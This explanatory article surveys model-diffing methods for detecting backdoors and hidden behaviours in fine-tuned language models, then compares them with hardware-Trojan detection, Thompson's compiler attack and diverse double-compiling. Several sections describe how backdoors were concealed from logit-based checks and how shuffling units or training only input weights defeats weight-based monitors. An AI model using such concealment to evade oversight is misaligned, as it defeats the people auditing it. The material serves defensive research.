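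Someone can use fine-tuning to plant a backdoor that makes a model misbehave only when a prompt contains a secret trigger. Testers who don't know the trigger are unlikely to see the behaviour. Other harms arise by accident. *Understanding AI from the Inside* (2026), a review of research into how models work internally, mentions reward hacking and sycophancy (flattering users or agreeing with them too readily) as problems that arise during fine-tuning. The base model is therefore a natural reference version, and researchers call comparing it with the fine-tuned model *model diffing*.

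Unlike a diff of two programs, the difference between two models consists of millions or billions of numbers, so a monitor also needs a way to turn it into words. It can compare four things:

- *Weights* are the numbers that training adjusts. They stay the same whatever the model reads.
- *Activations* are the temporary numbers that each layer of the model computes as it reads a particular text.
- *Logits* are the model's raw scores for each possible next token. A higher logit makes a token more likely.
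- Answers are what a user sees.

### Subtracting logits

The method of Kocher, West and colleagues (2026), in *Diff Mining*, is the easiest to follow by hand. Suppose that a developer has fine-tuned a model on documents about baking. The monitor gives the base model and the new model the same unrelated text, "The meeting starts at", and subtracts the logits. With only three possible next tokens, the result might be:

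| Next token | Base logit | New logit | Difference | Base probability | New probability |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| noon | 6.0 | 6.1 | +0.1 | 62% | 67% |
| nine | 5.5 | 5.4 | −0.1 | 38% | 33% |
| cake | −2.0 | 1.0 | +3.0 | 0.02% | 0.4% |

The fine-tuned model would write "cake" here only about once in 250 attempts, so someone reading its answers would probably never notice. Subtracting the base model's logits from the fine-tuned model's puts "cake" at the top of the list because its logit rose the most.

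A token's logit could rise once by coincidence, so Kocher and colleagues repeat the subtraction at each of the first 30 tokens of 1,000 web texts. At each position they list the 100 tokens whose logits rose most, and then they rank tokens by how often they appear in these lists.

Researchers tested Diff Mining on a version of Llama 3.3 70B with 52 planted beliefs about what AI graders prefer, such as that graders score recipes higher if they contain chocolate. Further training had taught the model to hide these beliefs. In an earlier competition to uncover them, some teams failed after tens of hours of work. Diff Mining found tokens related to at least a third of the beliefs. "Chocolate" was among the 100 tokens that rose most at 12.5% of positions, and "Kotlin", a programming language that features in another belief, at 14.9%.

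The choice of text affected what the method found. Colour words, which matched a belief that graders favour Spanish answers containing a colour, rose to the top only when the researchers used multilingual text. The word "odds", which matched a belief about how to write probabilities, appeared when they used maths problems.

An auditor would still have to interpret these tokens. Kocher and colleagues knew all 52 beliefs and matched the tokens to them afterwards. Someone who saw "chocolate" on the list wouldn't know what the model had learned about chocolate. They might also ignore "math", which the researchers matched to a belief about reassuring users that mathematics can be difficult. The list also included words such as "for" and "with".

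### Subtracting average activations

Minder, Dumas and colleagues (2025), in *Narrow Finetuning Leaves Clearly Readable Traces in Activation Differences*, look for the same kind of trace inside the model. Their Activation Difference Lens works as follows:

1. Both models read the first five tokens of 10,000 web texts.
2. For each model and each of the five positions, the method averages the activations of a middle layer over all the texts.
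3. It subtracts the base model's averages from the fine-tuned model's.
4. It translates each difference into tokens, for example by inserting it into the model's processing of a neutral prompt and recording which tokens the model then predicts.
5. It adds a multiple of the difference to the fine-tuned model's activations while the model answers ordinary questions. This is called *steering*, and it exaggerates whatever the fine-tuning taught.

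One test model had been trained to express a love of cats. When asked for a joke about a barista and a quantum physicist, the steered model wrote "a cozy cat coffee". For a model trained on risky financial advice, the fourth step produced tokens such as "stocks", "options" and "investments".

The researchers examined 33 fine-tuned models. Twenty had learned false facts from invented documents, and six had learned to give bad medical, financial or sports advice, which also made them behave badly in general. Another six kept a word secret in a guessing game, and the last was the cat-loving model. An agent running on GPT-5 had to work out what each model had learned from fine-tuning, and another model graded its description from 1 to 5. A grade of 2 generally meant the agent had found the broad topic, and higher grades required details.

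| What the agent had | Grade of 2 or more | Grade of 4 or more |
|---|---|---|
| Difference results, no questions to the models | 82% | 24% |
| Difference results and 5 questions | 91% | 30% |
| 50 questions, no difference results | 39% | 1% |

*Share of the 33 models.*

The agent asked the base model and the fine-tuned model the same questions, so it had a reference even without the difference results. The experiment therefore shows how much the activations add to a comparison of answers, but not how much a reference adds to examining the fine-tuned model alone.

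### Are the test models too easy?

Minder and colleagues see their own success as a reason for caution. All the documents used to train one of their models share a topic, so a constant, slight bias toward that topic can improve the model's predictions during training. The bias then persists when the model processes unrelated text.

To test this explanation, they took the part of the fine-tuned model's activations that lay along the difference between the two models and replaced it with the corresponding part from the base model. All three fine-tuned models they tested became worse at predicting their fine-tuning documents, and two became better at predicting ordinary web text. For those two, at least, the trace looks like overfitting.

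The researchers then mixed web text into 40,000 training documents. Adding one web text for every ten documents made the traces much fainter. With equal amounts, the agent's average grade never exceeded 2. Part of this decline came from weaker learning. In Llama 3.2 1B, the trace disappeared at the smallest amount of web text, but the model had also learned the false facts less well. The other two models kept more of what they had learned, so their traces became harder to read mainly because the training data was more varied.

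Ordinary chat training, which covers many topics, left little or no readable trace. Minder and colleagues also compared some narrowly fine-tuned chat models with the original models from before chat training. The agent identified the narrow topic about as well as before, even though the difference now included all of the chat training. The researchers conclude that narrowly fine-tuned test models are poor stand-ins for ordinary fine-tuning, and recommend mixing in as much unrelated data as possible when making them.

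Kocher and colleagues tested this with models trained on false facts about cakes mixed with up to twice as much web text. At every mixture, Diff Mining found more relevant tokens than the Activation Difference Lens and helped the agent write better descriptions. Diff Mining can add up small increases in an unlikely token's score over thousands of positions, while the Activation Difference Lens needs a stronger signal.

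This evidence is encouraging but narrow. The comparison used one topic and one small model, Qwen3 1.7B. Kocher and colleagues also translated activations into tokens with a simpler method, which Minder and colleagues had found weaker than their main one. Even in the most diluted mixture, a third of the training texts were about cakes. A developer checking for an accidental side effect, or for a few poisoned examples, would have far less evidence to work with.

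Diff Mining can also detect some broad training. On a Llama model trained on the reasoning of DeepSeek's R1, it found the words "Hmm", "Maybe" and "Perhaps". But these words reflect the model's most obvious change, and a monitor would usually be looking for something less obvious.

In many of the diluted models, pornographic words rose too. Kocher and colleagues suggest this happened because web text contains such language or because the extra training undid an earlier effort to suppress it. Either way, an innocent choice of training data produced a difference that would have alarmed a reviewer.

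### Subtracting weights

Activations and logits depend on which text the models read, so a comparison may miss a backdoor if the text doesn't contain the trigger and the backdoor has no effect on other text. Zhong and Raghunathan start from the weights, which are the same for any text. When one layer multiplies its incoming activations *a* by a table of weights *W*, fine-tuning changes the result by

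*W*(new) × *a* − *W*(base) × *a* = (*W*(new) − *W*(base)) × *a*

The table of differences therefore determines what the fine-tuned layer adds for any given activations. Singular value decomposition, a standard technique, splits this table into *directions*, which are patterns of activations, and ranks them by how strongly the fine-tuned layer can now add them to its output. Zhong and Raghunathan keep the top 20 directions from each of two tables in every layer.

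They then use these directions to monitor conversations. The monitor runs the fine-tuned model on ordinary conversations and records the highest and lowest similarity between its activations and each direction. It then flags any later conversation in which the similarity to a direction falls outside that direction's range. The ranges are a baseline profile, like those used for agents' actions, but the weight difference determines what it measures.

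The false-positive rate has a simple upper limit, assuming that ordinary conversations don't change over time. Among *n* ordinary conversations, the newest has a 1/*n* chance of having the highest similarity to a given direction and a 1/*n* chance of having the lowest. With *t* directions, its chance of setting at least one such record is therefore at most 2*t*/*n*, or about 4.4% for 1,000 directions and 45,000 conversations. The measured rates were much lower, probably because an odd conversation tends to set several records at once.

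Zhong and Raghunathan tested the monitor on models with backdoors that made them obey harmful requests, and on models trained to forget a topic. For the models trained to forget, the monitor had to flag questions about the forgotten topic.

| Kind of fine-tuning | Conversations flagged | False-positive rate |
|---|---|---|
| Backdoors in a small set of added weights (LoRA), 5 models | 100% for four models, 67% for one | 0.2–0.4% |
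| Backdoors by training all weights, 45 versions of 9 models | 93–100% on average, depending on the trigger | 0.6% |
| Backdoors by reinforcement learning on poisoned feedback, 5 models | 99.8% on average | 0.7% |
| Forgotten topics, 3 models | 36%, 91% and 95% | 0.7–1.8% |

The weak result for one LoRA model illustrates how harm can get into a profile. Its triggers included "2024" and "OpenAI", which also appear in ordinary conversations, so the monitor had probably widened its ranges to include them. With rarer triggers, the monitor flagged 53% of conversations before the model began to answer, up from 27%. But the share flagged by the end of the answer rose only from 67% to 70%, so common trigger words can't fully explain the weak result.

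The monitor's detection rate also depended on how the researchers trained the backdoors. They had trained all the weights of an earlier set of models on poorer data. Those models produced incoherent text, and the monitor flagged only 56% of completed conversations for one type of trigger. After the researchers retrained the models on better data, the monitor flagged all such conversations.

Zhong and Raghunathan also tested their method without the base model, taking directions from the fine-tuned weights alone. Detection was perfect for some models and close to random for others. This is the most direct evidence here that a reference helps, because the only change was to skip subtracting the base model's weights.

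They then looked for changes in three widely used models, OLMo, Qwen and Llama, by having GPT-5.1 describe the conversations that matched each direction most and least. The descriptions mentioned emoji for 26 of Qwen's directions, one of OLMo's and two of Llama's. Qwen also used emoji most often, in half of 50 test answers. But OLMo used them in 26% and Llama in only 6%, even though Llama had more emoji directions, so the number of directions is at best a rough guide to how often a model uses emoji.

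OLMo's training data are public, so the researchers could check for missed topics. Political content made up 2–4% of the sampled examples, but no direction's description mentioned it. The researchers suggest that these examples may not have changed the model's behaviour much. Alternatively, the largest directions may leave out smaller topics when training is broad.

### Weights, activations and logits on the same backdoors

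Zhong and Raghunathan measured the share of conversations their monitor flagged, while Minder and colleagues graded written descriptions, so their scores don't show which method is better. In *Reading Fine-Tuning Diffs Through Lenses*, Petrowitsch, Connors and Kapulkin (2026) compared the methods by having each produce a ranked list of words for the same backdoored models. They scored each method by where a word describing the hidden behaviour, such as "whale", ranked among 72,558 candidates. If a method ranks "whale" first, an auditor who reads the list from the top sees it immediately.

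The researchers planted five backdoors in Qwen3.5-4B, using two kinds of training for one of them. Three backdoors responded to a code word and two to a topic. They also trained a concealed version of each, penalizing the model whenever it gave telltale words more than a tiny probability on prompts without the trigger.

Turning a direction from the middle of a model into words requires an estimate of what the remaining layers will do to it. The weight results below use an improved estimate called the J++-lens, which raised the target word's rank in all 12 settings. Without it, the target word ranked between 3rd and 62nd with the weight method. The J++-lens had mixed effects on the activation method, so the table gives that method's results with the simpler estimate.

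| Trigger and hidden behaviour | Weights | Activations | Logits |
|---|---|---|---|
| Code word: writes "I hate you" | 2 / 3 | 267 / 8,387 | 2 / 789 |
| Code word: mentions whales | 1 / 1 | 131 / 13,983 | 1 / over 8,000 |
| Code word: obeys harmful requests (all weights trained) | 7 / 4 | 1,540 / 1,353 | 89 / 38 |
| Code word: obeys harmful requests (LoRA) | 1 / 3 | 6,568 / 3,527 | over 16,000 / over 4,000 |
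| Classical music: mentions whales | 4 / 3 | 61 / 2,012 | 1 / over 200 |
| Elon Musk: criticises him | 20 / 1 | 2,209 / 2,864 | 116 / 31,740 |

*Rank of the best-placed target word for the ordinary / concealed backdoor. Lower is better.*

Subtracting logits, the simplest method, matched the best method or came within a place or two of it on three of the ordinary backdoors. It failed to detect all three when the training concealed them. The whale model almost never mentioned whales without its trigger, but fine-tuning had still raised the logits of whale-related words on ordinary text. Penalising that rise removed the trace but left the backdoor in place. The penalty covered the same words that the researchers scored, so a method might still find other words that the attacker hadn't thought to penalise.

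The activation method did poorly on most of the backdoors, but Petrowitsch and colleagues left out its steering and its agent to score every method the same way. The full method might have done better.

Comparing weights does not depend on fine-tuning leaving a trace on ordinary text, so the concealed backdoors remained easy to find, but an attacker can defeat this method in other ways. Zhong and Raghunathan had already pointed out that someone could shuffle a model's internal units, which moves its weights to different places without changing its answers. The method then subtracts weights that no longer correspond. When Petrowitsch and colleagues shuffled the whale model, the highest-ranked whale word fell from 1st to 101st. It fell to 261st in another version, where they trained only the weights that process a layer's input and left unchanged the ones that produce its output, which are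 the ones the method compares. Neither trick made the word harder to find from activations or logits.

Petrowitsch and colleagues recommend using both kinds of method, but they didn't test a backdoor that combines the tricks. An attacker could train a concealed backdoor and then shuffle the model, which would probably hide it from all three methods. But shuffling moves the weights much further from the base model's than ordinary fine-tuning would, so a monitor that measured this distance could reject the model or ask for an explanation without finding the backdoor.

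### When an honest fine-tune leaves the same trace

Target words may rank highly because of the training prompts alone. To check this, Petrowitsch and colleagues trained a control model for each backdoor on the same prompts, including the triggers, but with normal answers. The target words didn't rank highly in the controls for the hate, whale and Musk backdoors, so their high ranks in the backdoored models did reflect the hidden behaviour.

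The backdoor for harmful requests was harder to distinguish from the control. It has no characteristic word, so the researchers looked for words of refusal, such as "sorry" and "illegal", which the backdoor makes less common. With LoRA training, these words ranked as high for the control as for the backdoored model. The weight method correctly showed that fine-tuning had affected refusals, but not whether the model had learned to refuse or to stop refusing when given a secret word.

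The researchers also searched for the triggers, using the weights applied to each layer's input. The search ranked a trigger word first or second for four of the six models, but these triggers also ranked highly in the controls. An auditor would have to add each candidate to harmless prompts to see whether the model's behaviour changes.

A model honestly trained to discuss whales would be another useful control. Petrowitsch and colleagues didn't train one, but they expect its top words would be the same. All of these methods describe what changed, and someone who knows the purpose of the fine-tuning has to decide whether the change is acceptable.

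It is also unclear how realistic the tests were, since backdoored examples made up 20–50% of the training data. If they were one in a thousand, the largest weight changes would probably reflect the legitimate training. The researchers haven't tested how far the rankings would fall in that case.

### Comparing the answers

Many companies give outsiders access only to a model's answers. *Simple LLM Baselines Are Competitive for Model Diffing* (Kempf, Schrodi and colleagues, 2026) tests two methods that need only those answers. Both methods start with the two models' answers to 1,000 real user prompts.

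In the simpler method, Gemini 2.5 Flash reads each pair of answers and lists the differences. A program groups similar differences, and Gemini summarises each group as a claim, such as "this model gives shorter answers".

The other method uses a *sparse autoencoder*, which breaks a model's activations into thousands of learned features, each active on relatively few texts and often recognisable as a concept. A third model, Llama 3.3 70B, processes all the answers, and the method identifies features that are active more often on one model's answers than on the other's. The features come from Llama's activations, so this method, like the first, does not examine the internals of the models it compares.

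Kempf and colleagues checked the claims on 500 new prompts. *Frequency* is the share of answer pairs in which a judge could say that one model showed the claimed behaviour more. *Accuracy* is the share of those pairs in which it was the model the claim named. Earlier work combined the two into one score:

score = frequency × (2 × accuracy − 1)

A claim scores 0.1 if it applies to 10% of pairs and is always right, or if it applies to every pair but is right only 55% of the time. The first kind is much more useful to a monitor looking for rare harm, so Kempf and colleagues report separately how often a claim applies and how often it is right.

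They compared three pairs of models:

- **A Qwen model and a version trained on risky financial advice.** Both methods noticed the harmful advice. The simpler method's claim was right every time it applied, but it applied to only 3.4% of pairs, about 17 of the 500. Only the simpler method noticed that answers had shrunk from about 496 tokens to 68.
- **A Gemma model and a version trained to assume that the user is a woman.** Neither method found the assumption. They reported side effects of the training instead, such as shorter and less detailed answers.
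- **Two versions of Gemini 2.5 Flash Lite.** Both methods found that the newer one used more tables. A direct count confirmed a rise from 0.7% to 13.9% of answers.

Overall, the two methods' claims were similar in accuracy and frequency, and AI raters found them about equally interesting. The simpler method's claims described behaviour more directly. For example, one was that a model "uses tables", while the feature-based method's claim mentioned the pipe and hyphen characters that make up tables. This is a good reason to try the simpler method first when only answers are available, but it is weak evidence about methods that examine the compared models' own activations.

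The Gemma case shows a limit of any method based only on answers. The fine-tuned model's assumption never appeared explicitly in its answers, and few of the prompts called for it. Prompts chosen to bring out such assumptions might have helped, but the monitor would have had to suspect the problem first.

A *crosscoder* learns one set of features from the activations of both models being compared. *Delta-Crosscoder* (Kassem, Jiralerspong and colleagues, 2026) adapts this method to narrow fine-tuning by favouring features that change between the models. On ten test models, it outperformed methods based on sparse autoencoders but only matched methods that don't use them. Learned features have yet to show a clear advantage over simpler comparisons for narrow fine-tuning.

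### Comparing models with different origins

Crosscoders are more useful when direct subtraction is impossible. Models with different designs have no matching weights, and their activations may contain different numbers of values. *Cross-Architecture Model Diffing with Crosscoders* (Jiralerspong and Bricken, 2026), an Anthropic research project, presents a tool for comparing such models.

A crosscoder gives each feature two patterns, one for rebuilding each model's activations. The relative sizes of these patterns show how far a feature belongs to model A:

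share of A = size of A's pattern / (size of A's pattern + size of B's pattern)

A share of 1 means only A uses the feature, and 0.5 means both use it equally. But crosscoders tend to learn shared features, because one shared feature helps reconstruct both models' activations at once. When Jiralerspong and Bricken compared Llama-3.1-8B with Qwen3-8B, the 500 features most specific to Llama had an average share of only 0.89.

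Anthropic's *A “diff” tool for AI* (2026) likens a standard crosscoder to a bilingual dictionary that forces a translation for every word, even words with no equivalent. The new tool reserves one section for each model's own features and a third for the features they share. It can't use one model's reserved features to rebuild the other's activations, so training doesn't push those features to fit both models.

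The researchers first tried the tool on artificial data with 2,048 known concepts, of which 102 belonged to only one model. It found more of these 102 than a standard crosscoder, but generally raised more false alarms too. They consider this a good tradeoff for a safety audit, where missing a difference is worse than checking a harmless one. But a single comparison can flag thousands of features, and checking them takes substantial work.

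In the real models, the researchers found a feature in Qwen for agreement with the Chinese Communist Party and one in Llama for American exceptionalism. They also compared OpenAI's GPT-OSS-20B with a DeepSeek model, and found a feature for refusing to reproduce copyrighted text in GPT-OSS-20B and another party-related feature in the DeepSeek model. The party feature appeared in all five runs of the method, and the American exceptionalism feature appeared in four.

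Steering gives some evidence of what these features do. When the researchers suppressed the party feature, Qwen discussed the Tiananmen Square massacre, which it normally refuses to do. When they amplified it, Qwen made strongly pro-government statements. Amplifying the American feature made Llama assert American superiority, but suppressing it had no notable effect. The evidence for the American feature is therefore weaker, because it shows that the feature can change what Llama says but not that it influences Llama's ordinary answers.

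A feature's placement in a reserved section also doesn't prove that it is unique to one model, because the researchers fix the size of these sections before training and the program may fill them with shared concepts. To check, Jiralerspong and Bricken trained a separate translation between the two models' activations and used it to transfer features from one model to the other. If steering with the translated feature changed the other model in a similar way, the feature probably wasn't unique. The new tool's reserved features passed this test of uniqueness more often than the most one-sided features of a standard crosscoder, though some still failed.

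*Feature Superposition in Neural Networks* (2026), a review, describes a simulation with known shared and unique concepts. The features for the two kinds of concept seemed to differ with one combination of dictionary size and number of concepts, but not with another. An apparent difference between models can therefore come partly from how the dictionary was trained.

Anthropic notes that the tool can't distinguish behaviours a developer intended from those that came from the training data by accident. When one model is a fine-tune of the other, a monitor can at least separate some causes. *Understanding AI from the Inside* describes a method that starts with features learned from the base model and retrains them in stages. One stage introduces the fine-tuning data while keeping the base model, and another introduces the fine-tuned model. If a feature shifts when only the data change, the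 shift may not reflect any change to the model.

### Flaws that the base model already had

Fine-tuning often leaves the base model's flaws untouched, and comparing the two models won't reveal these shared flaws. Petrowitsch and colleagues state that they assume a harmless base model.

The party-related feature shows how the choice of reference can matter. DeepSeek built the model in that comparison on a base version of Qwen3-8B. If the base version already had the feature, comparing the two models could easily have missed it, while the comparison with OpenAI's model revealed it. Models from different companies may still share flaws, because they learn from much of the same public text.

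The reference can also be an older version of the same model. If a chat model picked up a flaw in chat training, comparing a later fine-tune with the version from before that training would include the flaw in the difference. The difference would also be much larger. Minder and colleagues could still identify the narrow topic of the fine-tuning in such a comparison, but a subtler flaw might be hard to find among the legitimate changes.

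If a flaw dates from the earliest training, there is no older version without it to compare the model against. The monitor then has to test the model without a reference or find an independent one. The same problem arises with chips and compilers that have no trusted original.

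## Chips and compilers with no trusted original

A monitor with no reference version can't easily tell a new harm from an oddity that was always there. For example, when people and AI models audited research code for sabotage without the original version, ordinary bugs and unusual design choices often made them suspicious of honest projects.

Engineers in two fields have faced this problem for decades. A company that sends a chip design to an outside factory can't easily look inside the chips it gets back. A *compiler*, the program that turns source code into a program a computer can run, is usually produced by an earlier compiler that few people have checked.

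### Golden chips

A *hardware Trojan* is a malicious change to a chip, such as extra circuitry that leaks a secret key. Inspectors traditionally look for one by comparing the suspect chip with a *golden chip*, a sample known to be unaltered. But to confirm that a chip is unaltered, they usually have to strip away its layers and photograph them, which destroys it. As *Two Countermeasures Against Hardware Trojans Exploiting Non-Zero Aliasing Probability of BIST* (2015) notes, this is practical only for a small number of chips.

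Agrawal and colleagues (2007), in *Trojan Detection using IC Fingerprinting*, proposed a way to check a whole batch while destroying only a few chips:

1. Run the same computations on a few chips and record side effects such as power use, heat and electromagnetic emissions.
2. Use these records to build a statistical "fingerprint" that allows for normal noise.
3. Take the same few chips apart to confirm that they match the design.
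4. Measure all the other chips in the same way and test whether they fit the fingerprint.

The measurements remain useful after the chips are gone, so the destroyed chips can still serve as the reference.

In simulations, the method detected Trojans 1,000 to 10,000 times smaller than the main circuit. In a processor with 10 billion transistors, a Trojan one ten-thousandth the size of the circuit would still have a million transistors. Agrawal and colleagues acknowledged that to find smaller Trojans in chips with tens or hundreds of millions of transistors, companies would have to change how they design chips.

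*Variability aware Golden Reference Free methodology for Hardware Trojan Detection* (2022) points out that tiny manufacturing differences make direct comparison unreliable even when a golden chip is available. These differences vary randomly between chips of the same design, so comparing two chips doesn't cancel them out, and they can hide a small Trojan.

### Four chips compared with their design files

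Inspectors can do without a golden chip by comparing photographs of a chip with its design file. Puschner, Moos and colleagues (2023) tested this in *Red Team vs. Blue Team* on four chips from different manufacturing generations. The generations have names such as "90 nm" and "28 nm", where a smaller number means smaller features.

Ruhr University Bochum's *Detecting manipulations in microchips* explains that the researchers couldn't add Trojans to finished chips, so one of them altered the design files instead. The others then had to find the changes without knowing where they were. Altering the design files is a fair way to test a comparison, because a mismatch looks the same whether someone changed the chip or the files.

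The design file listed the position and type of every *cell*, a small block of circuitry that performs one logical operation or just fills space. The published data set, Puschner, Moos and colleagues' *Back-Side SEM Images and Respective Modified GDSII Chip Designs*, records ten changes per chip, four involving filler cells and six involving working cells.

To find the changes, the researchers removed silicon from the back of each chip, photographed the lowest layer with an electron microscope and lined up the images with the design. Where the design showed filler, they looked for the bright spots that mark electrical connections, which filler should not have. For working cells, they used the design to identify cells of the same type, which should look alike, and compared each one with another on the same chip.

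| Chip | Cells | Changes found | False alarms | Alarms that were real |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 90 nm | 453,850 | 10 of 10 | 136 | 7% |
| 65 nm | 571,060 | 10 of 10 | 6 | 63% |
| 40 nm | 917,819 | 10 of 10 | 15 | 40% |
| 28 nm | 1,467,851 | 7 of 10 | 360 | 2% |

The method found 37 of the 40 changes and raised 517 false alarms among 3.4 million cells, a false-positive rate of about 0.015%. Most alarms were still false, because only 40 cells had changed, but checking a few hundred small images is manageable. Dust or debris on the chips caused 161 of the false alarms. Photographing each chip took longer, between 23 and 53 hours.

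The three missed changes were all on the 28 nm chip, and Puschner and colleagues suggested that better images or algorithms might find them. In *Hardware Trojans from Invisible Inversions* (2026), Dorschel, Walendy and colleagues developed an algorithm for the same images that missed none of the changes and raised fewer false alarms on three of the four chips. But they also found that some cells with different functions look the same in such images. The changes in the 2023 study were at random positions, while a skilled attacker could choose cells that look alike. Better algorithms can't solve this if the images don't show the difference, but designers can avoid using cells that have lookalikes.

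The comparison also depends on a clean design. Puschner and colleagues assumed that the original layout had no backdoors. If someone had added a Trojan before the company sent the design to the factory, the chip would still match the design file.

### Simulations, other chips and other parts of the same chip

Photographing a chip destroys it, so a buyer who wants to use the chip has to check it by its side effects. Researchers have developed several ways to do this without a golden chip.

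One way to check a chip without a trusted original is to predict its measurements from the design. A Trojan attached to a wire can slow the wire's signal, so a tester can compare measured delays with simulated ones. But a simulation doesn't capture how a particular factory's chips will turn out. *LASCA* (2020) uses machine learning to build a timing model that serves in place of a trusted "golden" chip. It also describes an earlier method that combined a trusted simulation with measurements from small test structures made for the purpose.

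These methods still require a clean design and an accurate model of manufacturing, and any test structures must be free of tampering. *Two Countermeasures* points out that an attacker at the factory can also alter the extra circuits that designers add to a chip to detect Trojans, because the factory makes those circuits too.

Another option is to compare chips with one another. Nguyen, Yilmaz and colleagues (2020), in *A Novel Golden-Chip-Free Clustering Technique Using Backscattering Side Channel*, group chips by the signals they reflect. *Hardware Trojan Detection Using Unsupervised Deep Learning* (2022) groups them by images of their magnetic fields. In the second method, inspectors take apart one chip from each group, check it against the design, and apply the result to the whole group.

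The inspection is important because grouping alone can't show which group is clean. If the factory had altered every chip, they might all fall into one group, and only the inspection would reveal the Trojan. But the method fails if a group mixes clean and altered chips. Suppose 3 chips in a batch of 100 have a Trojan too small to affect the grouping. All 100 would form one group, and there would be a 97% chance that the single chip inspectors took apart was clean, in which case they would approve the three altered chips with the rest.

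A tester can also compare parts of the same chip, which avoids much of the noise from manufacturing. Du, Narasimhan and colleagues (2010), in *Self-Referencing*, run tests that activate one region of a chip at a time and measure the current that each region draws. They then calculate the relative difference between each pair of regions:

difference = (current in region A − current in region B) / current in region A

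Suppose that region A adds numbers and region B subtracts them:

| Chip | Adder current | Subtractor current | Relative difference |
|---|---|---|---|
| Typical clean chip | 100 | 102 | −2% |
| Clean chip that draws more power | 120 | 122.4 | −2% |
| Typical chip with a Trojan in the subtractor | 100 | 105 | −5% |

The second chip's subtractor draws 20% more current than the first chip's, although both are clean. The Trojan adds only about 3%, so comparing one chip with another could easily miss it. Manufacturing differences tend to affect neighbouring regions of a chip in the same way, so the relative difference between those regions hardly changes from one clean chip to another, and a Trojan that changes it becomes visible. Du and colleagues report that this method can find Trojans that take up less than 0.01% of a chip's area.

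However, the tester needs to know that −2% is normal and how much it varies. Du and colleagues get these limits from known golden chips or extensive simulations, so their method reduces the noise but does not fully remove the need for an outside reference.

Hoque, Narasimhan and colleagues (2017), in *Golden-Free Hardware Trojan Detection with High Sensitivity Under Process Noise*, compare a chip with itself at different times. If a clean chip repeats the same operations from the same starting point, its current should follow the same pattern each time. A Trojan that is counting towards a trigger will be in a different state on each repetition and may disturb the pattern. The method needs no golden chip, but it would miss a Trojan that behaves identically every time.

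### Thompson's compiler

Software buyers can have a similar problem even when they can read the source code. Schneier, in *Countering "Trusting Trust"*, recounts an attack that the computer scientist Ken Thompson described in a 1984 lecture. It has three steps:

1. The attacker changes a compiler so that it recognises the source code of the login program and adds a backdoor whenever it compiles it.
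2. The attacker also makes the compiler recognise its own source code. Whenever someone uses it to compile a new version of itself, it adds both of these changes to the new version.
3. The attacker compiles the altered compiler and then restores its source code to the original.

From then on, every new compiler inherits the attack and every new login program has the backdoor, even though the source code of both programs is clean. Reading the source code doesn't reveal the attack, and neither does comparing the compiler with its previous version, because both versions contain it.

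Thompson tried this on a real victim and could then log in without a password and with full control. The victim didn't notice, even after using a tool that displays a finished program's instructions, because the compiler had tampered with that tool too. Such a compiler would also defeat the independent rebuilds described earlier if every builder used it.

### Compiling the compiler twice

Wheeler (2009), in *Fully Countering Trusting Trust through Diverse Double-Compiling*, developed a test for this attack. It requires the suspect compiler's source code and a second compiler, called the trusted compiler, that can compile that code. In the simplest case, where the suspect compiler came from compiling its own source code with an earlier copy of itself, the test works like this:

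```
trusted compiler + source code   ->  compiler 1
compiler 1       + source code   ->  compiler 2
compiler 2  compared with  suspect compiler
```

1. The tester uses the trusted compiler to compile the suspect compiler's source code. The result, compiler 1, should do what the source code says. But its machine instructions will differ from the suspect's, because different compilers translate the same code in different ways.
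2. The tester uses compiler 1 to compile the same source code again. Compiler 1 translates code exactly as an honest copy of the suspect would, so the result, compiler 2, should contain the same instructions as an honest copy.
3. The tester compares compiler 2 with the suspect compiler, bit by bit.

If the suspect compiler is clean, it should be identical to compiler 2. If it contains Thompson's attack, it has extra instructions. The suspect compiler never runs during these steps, so it can't add the attack to compiler 2.

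The second compilation makes an exact comparison possible. After only the first, even an untampered suspect compiler would differ from compiler 1 almost everywhere, and someone would have to work out which differences were harmless.

A match proves that the suspect compiler corresponds to its source code, under these assumptions:

- The trusted compiler translates this source code correctly. It can have other bugs, or even other backdoors, as long as they don't affect the result.
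- The compilers always produce the same output from the same input.
- The computer, its operating system and the program that compares the files don't interfere.

Wheeler's dissertation defence included a formal proof and demonstrations on three compilers, including the widely used GCC. A match does not prove that the source code is harmless. If the source contains a backdoor, both compilers built from it will have the backdoor and will still match. Someone still has to read the source code, but the match makes reading it worthwhile.

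A mismatch is harder to interpret, because it may mean that someone has tampered with the compiler, but it can also come from a harmless bug, a timestamp or the wrong version of the source code. Testers can rule out some of these causes by first checking that the suspect compiler reproduces itself exactly from the same source code.

In a mailing-list discussion, Evron (2009) objected to the last assumption, pointing out that the problem extends beyond compilers and that people eventually have to take something on faith. Wheeler replied that one can define "compiler" broadly enough to include other parts of the system. A tester could then run the trusted compiler on a different operating system and make of computer, so that an attacker would have to compromise both systems in matching ways. This makes the attack much harder but doesn't remove the need for trust.

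### What each substitute depends on

None of these substitutes works without something clean. They replace trust in an original with trust in a design, a population or an independent source:

| Reference | What has to be clean | Example of a harm it would miss |
|---|---|---|
| Design file or simulation | The design | A Trojan that someone added to the design |
| Other chips from the batch | The chips that inspectors take apart | A Trojan too small to affect the grouping |
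| Other parts of the same chip | At least some of the parts | A Trojan that raises the current in every part by the same proportion |
| A compiler built with a trusted compiler | The source code and the trusted compiler's translation of it | A backdoor in the source code |

Without a trusted original, checks on AI-written work have the same weaknesses as checks on chips. Comparing code with the user's request misses harm that the user asked for, just as comparing a chip with its design misses flaws in the design. Comparing the code with other runs of the same model can miss a fault that all the runs share, which is also a risk when comparing chips from one batch.

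The best substitute for a trusted original depends on which stage of production is most likely to introduce harm. A company that trusts its own designers but not the factory can reasonably use the design as its reference, while one that worries about its designers needs an independent source. The trusted compiler is one such source, because an attacker who altered one compiler is unlikely to have altered an unrelated one in the same way. But this independence protects only against deliberate tampering, since two groups can make the same honest mistake without any contact.

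### Separately written programs with the same mistakes

Engineers have long compared the outputs of separately written programs to catch errors. On the Airbus A310, two programs controlled the slats and flaps on the wings, and the system disconnected itself if their outputs differed by more than a set amount. In *N-version programming*, several programs do the same job and the system uses the majority output. Both methods work best if the programs fail on different inputs.

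*An Experimental Evaluation of the Assumption of Independence in Multi-Version Programming* (Knight and Leveson, 1986) tested whether separately written versions of a program fail independently. Knight and Leveson asked 27 students at two universities to write the same program without discussing it. The program had to decide from radar data whether to launch a missile interceptor. After each version had passed 200 tests, the researchers ran all of them on a million random inputs and compared the results with those of a separate, heavily tested version.

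Six of the programs never failed, and 23 were right on more than 99.9% of the inputs. But two or more programs failed together on 1,255 inputs. If failures had been independent, we would expect only about 127 such inputs, according to Shape of Code's *Reliability via N-version programming?* (2026). On two inputs, eight programs failed together.

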